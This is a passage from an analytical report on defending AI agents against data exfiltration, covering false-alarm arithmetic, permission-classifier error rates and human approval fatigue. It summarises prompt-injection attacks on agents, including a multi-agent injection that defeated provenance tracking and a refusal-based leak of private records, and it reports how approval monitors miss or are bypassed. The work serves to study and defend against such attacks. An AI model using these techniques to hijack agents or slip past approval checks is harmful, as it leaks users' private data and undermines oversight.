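| A plain secret sent to the attacker's own domain | Yes, if the filter knows the secret or its pattern | Yes | Yes |
| An encoded or split secret sent to the attacker's own domain | Usually not | Yes | Yes |
| A plain secret sent to the attacker's account on an approved service | Yes, if the filter knows the secret or its pattern | No | Only if the labels distinguish accounts |
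| An encoded or split secret sent to that account | Usually not | No | Only if the labels distinguish accounts |
| A private fact, in ordinary words, sent to a familiar contact | Seldom | No | Yes, if someone has labelled the fact |
| A secret spelled out by a choice of approved pages | No | No | Not completely |

Searching the content adds almost nothing to checking the destination when an agent needs only a few destinations and attackers have no account on any of them. It is mainly useful on approved services that anyone can join, where it can catch careless attacks and honest mistakes, but a competent attacker will encode the secret to evade the search.

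Some leaks can be recognised only by checking the data and the destination together. `hotel.example` should receive Ana's loyalty-card number but not her payslip. A content filter that blocked the card number would also prevent her booking, while a domain list that approved the hotel would let the payslip through. *The Framing Gap* describes a secret that must go to one host but not another as the harder and more realistic case, and leaves it for later work. A rule like those in FIDES could handle this case by listing the hotel as a permitted reader of only the card number.

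Tracking can fail too, and a plain check on the recipient may then be the better defence. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed how tracking can fail using three agents that each ran CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. One agent fetched the data, which contained hidden instructions, and the coordinating agent pasted the summary into its request to a third agent. That agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so it also emailed the applicants' details to an outside address. A rule that trusts addresses supplied by the user would probably have accepted this one, because the record of where it came from had been lost between agents. A warning about first-time recipients would have flagged it. The researchers propose passing instructions and data between agents separately, which stopped every attack in their tests and reduced the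 two strongest models' task completion by less than one additional percentage point.

Leaks are hardest for a content filter to catch when the agent sends nothing private. In another attack by Shim and colleagues, an outsider gives the agent a page that mixes real and invented records about someone and asks it to clean the page up. The agent refuses to delete the real records, revealing which ones they are. In a live test with Gmail and Notion, this exposed 34.7% of the private items despite a defence that had a model look for privacy violations. Their own system, FlowSeal, reduced the figure to zero. It intercepts every attempt to write or share, labels records by their owner, and has a separate model compare the proposed change with the protected records. Across all their tests, it leaked at most 3.3% of the items and completed 72.4% of legitimate tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best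 of the other defences.

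## How many false alarms new destinations cause, and who should decide

Suppose an office worker's agent makes 200 web requests a day, and 5% of them go to hosts it has never contacted. A warning about new hosts would then appear ten times a day. Suppose also that attackers hijack the agent once per 1,000 user-days (a user-day is one person using an agent for one day), and that 90% of hijacks send data to a new host. These figures are all assumptions. Over 1,000 user-days they give:

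`honest alerts = 1,000 × 200 × 5% = 10,000`

`real alerts = 1 × 90% = 0.9`

About one alert in 11,000 is real. Suppose the software raises an alert only if it also finds a second sign of theft, and that this removes 98% of the false alarms and none of the real alerts. That leaves 200 false alarms and the same 0.9 real alerts, so about one alert in 220 is real.

| | New host alone | New host and a second sign |
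|---|---|---|
| Alerts for each user | Ten a day | One every five days |
| Alerts for each real one | About 11,000 | About 220 |
| Time to review that many, at ten seconds each | About 31 hours | About 37 minutes |

With the first system, a worker would spend more than four working years, on average, dismissing false alerts before seeing a real one. A new host still multiplies the odds of theft by 18, as in the earlier example with Bayes' rule, but thefts here are 20 times rarer. For a general-purpose agent, novelty alone is therefore too weak a reason to block a request or interrupt someone. It can still help decide which requests to log in detail or send to a slower check.

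The number of false alarms depends on the agent's job. A research agent that sends half its requests to new hosts would raise 100 alerts a day, and about one in 111,000 would be real. An agent that pays a fixed set of suppliers might contact a new host only once in 20 working days. On the same assumptions about hijacks, about one in 57 of its alerts would be real, and a person could reasonably review every one.

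The second sign must be rare in legitimate visits to new hosts. Private data in the request might qualify, as might an address that came from an email rather than from the user. Rarity across the company would work less well, because a site that is new to one employee is often new to most of the others. Assuming that the second sign removes no real alerts is also optimistic. If it missed half of the thefts, for instance because the agent had encoded the data, only about one alert in 445 would be real, and the system would flag 45% of hijacks instead of 90%.

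### Measured error rates

Some measured rates come from Claude Code's auto mode, which uses a two-stage classifier to judge an action partly by whether its destination lies inside the user's declared trust boundary. The first stage quickly answers yes or no and leans towards blocking. The second reasons more carefully about whatever the first flagged. Anthropic tested both stages on three sets of actions.

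| Test | Number of actions | Error rate after first stage | Error rate after both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| False alarms on real tool calls by Anthropic employees | 10,000 | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Misses on artificial attempts to steal data | 1,000 | 1.8% | 5.7% |
| Misses on real "overeager" actions, which went beyond what the user had authorised | 52 | 6.6% | 17% |

The second stage does roughly what the second sign does in the example. It removes about 95% of the false alarms, but it also lets through about 4% of the attempted thefts that the first stage caught. The 17% figure is uncertain because it comes from only 52 actions, and the true rate could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%.

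If the classifier reviewed all 200 daily requests in the example with these error rates, it would raise about 800 false alarms per 1,000 user-days and catch 0.94 hijacks, so about one alarm in 850 would be real. That is about 13 times better than novelty alone, but each user would still trigger nearly one false alarm a day. This rate is tolerable in auto mode because most false alarms make the agent retry and never reach a person.

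In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had detected the danger but was wrong about whether the user had agreed to it. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed change to shared code) hasn't necessarily agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's history. The same error could happen with destinations. If Ana tells her agent to "sort out the hotel", a classifier might treat this as permission to give her card number to any site that looks like a hotel's.

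Vague requests can raise both kinds of error. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested auto mode on 128 server-administration tasks whose scope or risk was deliberately left unclear. The classifier missed 70.3% of the actions it reviewed that went too far, and blocked 31.9% of the acceptable ones. The overall miss rate was 81.0%, partly because auto mode lets the agent edit files inside the project without review. The researchers say their tasks differ too much from ordinary use to contradict Anthropic's figures, and they weren't testing theft. But the false-alarm rate rose from 0.4% to 31.9% with the type of work, so a rate measured for programmers can't be applied to, say, a sales team whose agents write to new customers every day.

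OpenAI has a similar reviewer for Codex. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) gives an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions from the company's internal use. Of these, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox and needed no approval. The reviewer, a separate agent, approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. Codex found a safer alternative in four of those seven cases and stopped to ask the user in three. At 200 actions a day, a user would get about one question every 17 days, compared with about 14 a day under manual approval.

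In tests with artificial cases, the reviewer denied 90.3% of overeager actions and 99.3% of actions caused by prompt injection. To measure unnecessary denials, OpenAI used real requests that its employees had approved, and the reviewer approved 99.1% of them. This measure assumes that the employees were right to approve the requests, which is doubtful if they were clicking quickly. OpenAI's testers also misled the reviewer into approving commands, and the company says not to treat the reviewer as a guarantee.

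### Running the command before approving it

A command's text may not show where it will send data, so Caper, a system from *Shall We Approve?* (Wu, Chen and colleagues, 2026), runs each command in a sandbox with no network connection before deciding whether to accept the result. Caper records which files the command read, what it changed and which addresses it tried to contact. A model then compares a short report of these effects with the user's request. If the model rejects the command, Caper restores the earlier state.

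In one example, an agent ran a script that was supposed to check which software packages a project needed. Caper's report showed that the script had read a credentials file and then tried to contact outside addresses, and the model blocked it. Neither fact appeared in the command. A package check has no obvious need for credentials, so reading them is the kind of second sign that could make a new-destination alert useful.

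Wu and colleagues also tested Caper on 102 tasks in which an ordinary-looking tool secretly damaged a file. Harm occurred in 7.8% of the tasks with Caper and in at least 35.3% with each of the six other systems. Each task had a harmless twin with the same request and command, and Caper wrongly blocked 1.0% of the twins. The approvers that read only text tended to block both the dangerous command and its twin because they could not distinguish them. None of these tasks involved theft. A second benchmark included information leaks among other harms, and Caper's overall rate of harmful outcomes on it was 6.7%, compared with at least 14.8% for the others.

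### What people do with frequent warnings

A person has to review any alarm that the software can't resolve, and people pay less attention as warnings accumulate. This is one reason OpenAI decided against a strict list of trusted sites, which it feared would train users to click through warnings. OpenAI's own check also causes false alarms because, according to a company help page, users must confirm every link to a website that has opted out of being catalogued, even if the link is harmless.

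According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97% of the permission prompts they see. The company had reported 93% in March. These rates don't show that users are careless, because a careful reviewer would also approve nearly everything if nearly everything were safe. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents before starting work. Anthropic takes this as a sign that people examine plans more closely, though a user may also reject a safe plan because they want the work done differently.

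The ways people avoid prompts are clearer evidence of fatigue. According to the same post, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started with permission checks switched off. Trębacz and colleagues found that a sizeable minority of Codex users inside OpenAI had pre-approved every command beginning with "python", which can run almost any program. A strict check can therefore leave users with less protection than a looser one if it irritates them enough to turn it off.

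*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that user review contributed to the problem in 105. In 80 of these, the user had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the prompt hadn't given the user enough information to judge the action, usually because it showed a command and not what the command would do to the files. (Some reports fall into both groups.)

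Software practitioners quoted in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described clicking through familiar prompts and sometimes skipping review under time pressure. These habits are a problem for any system that learns from past approvals. If a user approves a new site because they are in a hurry, the software may record the site as trusted and never prompt the user about it again.

*From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites usage data showing that experienced Claude Code users both turned on automatic approval and interrupted the agent more often. They may prefer to watch the work and step in when something looks wrong. Watching won't stop most data theft, because a single request takes less than a second and may leave nothing unusual on the screen.

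### People compared with a classifier

Anthropic published its comparison of human and automatic review in August 2026, in the post that announced auto mode as the default for most subscribers. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers, who worked in a test environment. They knew they were being evaluated in a coding study, but not that the study was about permission prompts. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded the tester's answer. The command never ran, even if the tester approved it.

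The testers refused the dangerous command in 143 of 1,053 cases, or 13.6%. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%.

| | Auto mode blocked it | Auto mode allowed it |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

Requiring approval from both would have stopped 943 commands, only six more than auto mode alone. Testers tired within sessions, catching about 17% of the dangerous commands early on and about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed level. Fatigue explains only part of the result, since testers approved about five in six dangerous commands even early in a session.

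The testers had less at stake than people working on their own projects, and they may have assumed that nothing in a test environment could hurt them. But people who know they are being evaluated usually take more care. The commands were obviously dangerous, which probably made them easier for the classifier to catch than a theft disguised as routine work. Anthropic also reports the classifier's 89% catch rate without a new false-alarm rate. The 89% is hard to interpret without knowing how many safe commands the same version would have blocked, since a classifier that blocked every command would have scored 100%. The 0.4% false-alarm rate from March may no longer apply, because Anthropic has since changed the classifier.

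Anthropic has a commercial interest in the study's result. It sells Claude Code, paid for the study and used the result to justify a new default. It also promotes auto mode as a way to leave its models working for hours, and reports that business customers who adopted it produce about 25% more pull requests. This is a reason for someone else to repeat the study with ordinary users and their own files. It doesn't make the counts wrong, though, and the gap between 13.6% and 89% is too large for small design flaws to explain.

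The other evidence in the post is less convincing. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged, serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. But users chose their own mode, and Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* recommends manual approval for sensitive work and unfamiliar code, where serious harm is more likely anyway.

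An outside company, Trajectory Labs, made 720 injection attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. But even with no permission checks, only 0.09% succeeded on average against Anthropic's latest models, so the test measures the models' resistance more than the classifier's performance. A two-week exercise with Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested the classifier more directly by inserting artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions. The classifier missed 12% of these attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic improved it.

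Willison accepts that auto mode is better than constantly asking people to approve actions, but notes that 11% of the dangerous commands still got through and wants more independent confirmation. Rehberger has since bypassed the classifier, according to The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*, and says Anthropic told him that auto mode is a convenience feature, not a security guarantee.

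### When people judge better

People did much better in an independent experiment with fewer and clearer prompts. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, analysed data from 113 people from outside the software industry who supervised an assistant through a scripted, simulated day. Sessions averaged about 11 minutes. The assistant attempted 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for, such as reading private messages or publicly announcing the user's travels. Each prompt described the action in plain language, including the data, recipient or amount involved.

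| How the participants gave permission | Prompts per person | Unrequested actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Approved or refused every action | 18.0 | 59.6% |
| Decided only the actions that a model passed on to them | 10.0 | 53.9% |
| Wrote four standing rules first, each "allow", "ask" or "never" | 10.9 | About 40% |

Participants who decided on every action themselves blocked more than four times the share that Anthropic's testers did. The wording of the prompts may explain part of the difference, and frequency probably explains another part. More than a third of the actions in Yan's study were ones to refuse, whereas Anthropic's testers saw one bad command among dozens of routine ones. A real agent's user is in a situation much closer to the testers', or a worse one. The actions also differed. Some of Yan's were fairly harmless, such as buying a $12 travel insurance policy, so participants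 may have allowed them because they liked the idea.

In the second group, the model referred all seven unrequested actions to participants. Better detection would not have helped, because participants approved every action that went ahead. The standing rules were less effective than hoped for a similar reason. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed the decision, and then approved two-thirds of the unrequested actions when prompted.

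In the opening example, a warning about new hosts flags 90% of hijacks. If users refuse 13.6% of the flagged thefts, the warning stops only 12% of hijacks. If they refuse 59.6%, the rate in Yan's study, it stops 54%. With a classifier that caught 89% of the flagged thefts, it would stop 80%. None of these catch rates was measured on warnings about destinations, so the results are only illustrative. But they show that who judges the flagged requests can matter more than how many hijacks the warning flags. For a careless user, flagging 100% of hijacks instead of 90% would stop only about one percentage point more of them.

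Software is therefore better suited to making the first check on most flagged requests, because there are so many and nearly all are legitimate. A person is more useful when the decision depends on something only that person knows. For the hotel request that contains Ana's card number, a classifier can establish that the hotel is real and that she asked about it, but not whether she wants to share the number for a discount. In a similar example from OpenAI, a link to a car-search site would reveal that the user lives in London, which the user may be happy to share because it makes the results more relevant.

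The question should then show what will be sent and who will receive it, as OpenAI's Safe Url does when it asks for confirmation. Ana can answer "Send your loyalty-card number, 48213, to hotel.example?" in a few seconds, but she would need longer to check a long web address with the number somewhere in the middle. For an employer's own suppliers and services, an administrator may know better than she does whether a new domain is genuine, and can decide once for everyone.

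### Matching the response to the channel

Software can often undo a mistake that stays on its own machine, as Caper does when it restores a damaged project, but it can't bring back data that has reached someone else. Wu and colleagues disconnect the network during the trial run for this reason. The response to an unfamiliar destination therefore has to come before the data leaves. False alarms disrupt honest users more on some channels than on others, and the response can be stricter where the disruption is small.

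| Channel | Response to an unfamiliar destination | Cost of a false alarm |
|---|---|---|
| Image or link preview | Don't load it | A missing picture |
| Page fetch | Send the agent to another source | Some time, and perhaps a worse source |
| Email | Hold the message, then send or cancel it | A delay |
| Webhook | Have a person register the address once | One approval during setup |
| Publishing or sharing code | Ask a person each time | An interruption |

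Images are the easiest case because an answer is usually just as useful without them. Few people would mind much if 10,000 legitimate images failed to load for every theft prevented, but being asked about each one would be intolerable.

When an agent tries to fetch a page, the software can often refuse the address and let the agent look elsewhere, since many facts appear on more than one site. In OpenAI's internal use, Codex continued successfully after more than half of the denials it received, although those denials covered all kinds of actions. Refusing works less well when the user wants a particular page, such as a small guesthouse's price list. The user's request is then evidence that the visit is legitimate, and asking the user a short question is reasonable if the address carries private data.

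Sending the agent elsewhere is also risky, because it may choose a worse destination. In one incident inside Anthropic, Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. Auto mode blocked this and asked the user what to do. *Let the Agent Do It?* recommends that tools distinguish between refusing one action and refusing a whole approach. For exfiltration, the refusal should cover sending the data to any outside party, because a hijacked agent that is refused only one address can try another.

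Delaying email works well because the sender seldom needs an immediate reply. If Ana's agent writes to ten new hotels and the mail service holds each message for ten minutes, all ten wait at the same time. The agent continues with other work, and the hotels won't notice. When the agent browses, it needs each page before it can decide what to do next, so each new site held for ten minutes adds ten minutes to the task, and ten sites add 100.

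A ten-minute hold can stop a theft only if someone or something checks the message during that time. A slower model could read it, or Ana could get a notification and cancel it. The mail service might also detect that dozens of other agents have written to the same unknown address since the first message arrived. Some legitimate messages are urgent, such as a note telling a new client that Ana is running late, so she needs a way to release them early.

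Recalling an email is much less reliable than holding it. A company can often remove a message from a mailbox on its own system, but it can't make an outside mail server delete a message that server has already accepted. A thief's address will usually be outside, so in practice the company can't recall a stolen file once it releases the email from the hold.

Webhooks need a different approach because programs call them repeatedly. An agent that posts a report every hour makes 8,760 calls a year, and nobody would check them all. But the address seldom changes, so a person can approve it once and have the software refuse any other. The approval must cover both the full address, including the part that identifies the workspace, and the account whose key the agent uses. A person must give it, because a hijacked agent that could register its own webhooks would add the attacker's. New registrations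 should be rare enough that an unexpected one deserves close inspection, just as a new host is a stronger warning sign for the agent that pays a fixed set of suppliers.

Publishing is harder to delay or redirect, and people outside the team may copy the material within minutes, so asking the user each time may be worth the interruption. Anthropic lets users add a human checkpoint for pull requests and for pushes, which upload code to a shared project. In Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production*, an engineer at the vehicle company Nuro says he uses auto mode for all his own coding but goes back to manual approval when Claude reviews a colleague's pull request, so that he can read each review before it goes out under his name. He answers far fewer prompts this way.
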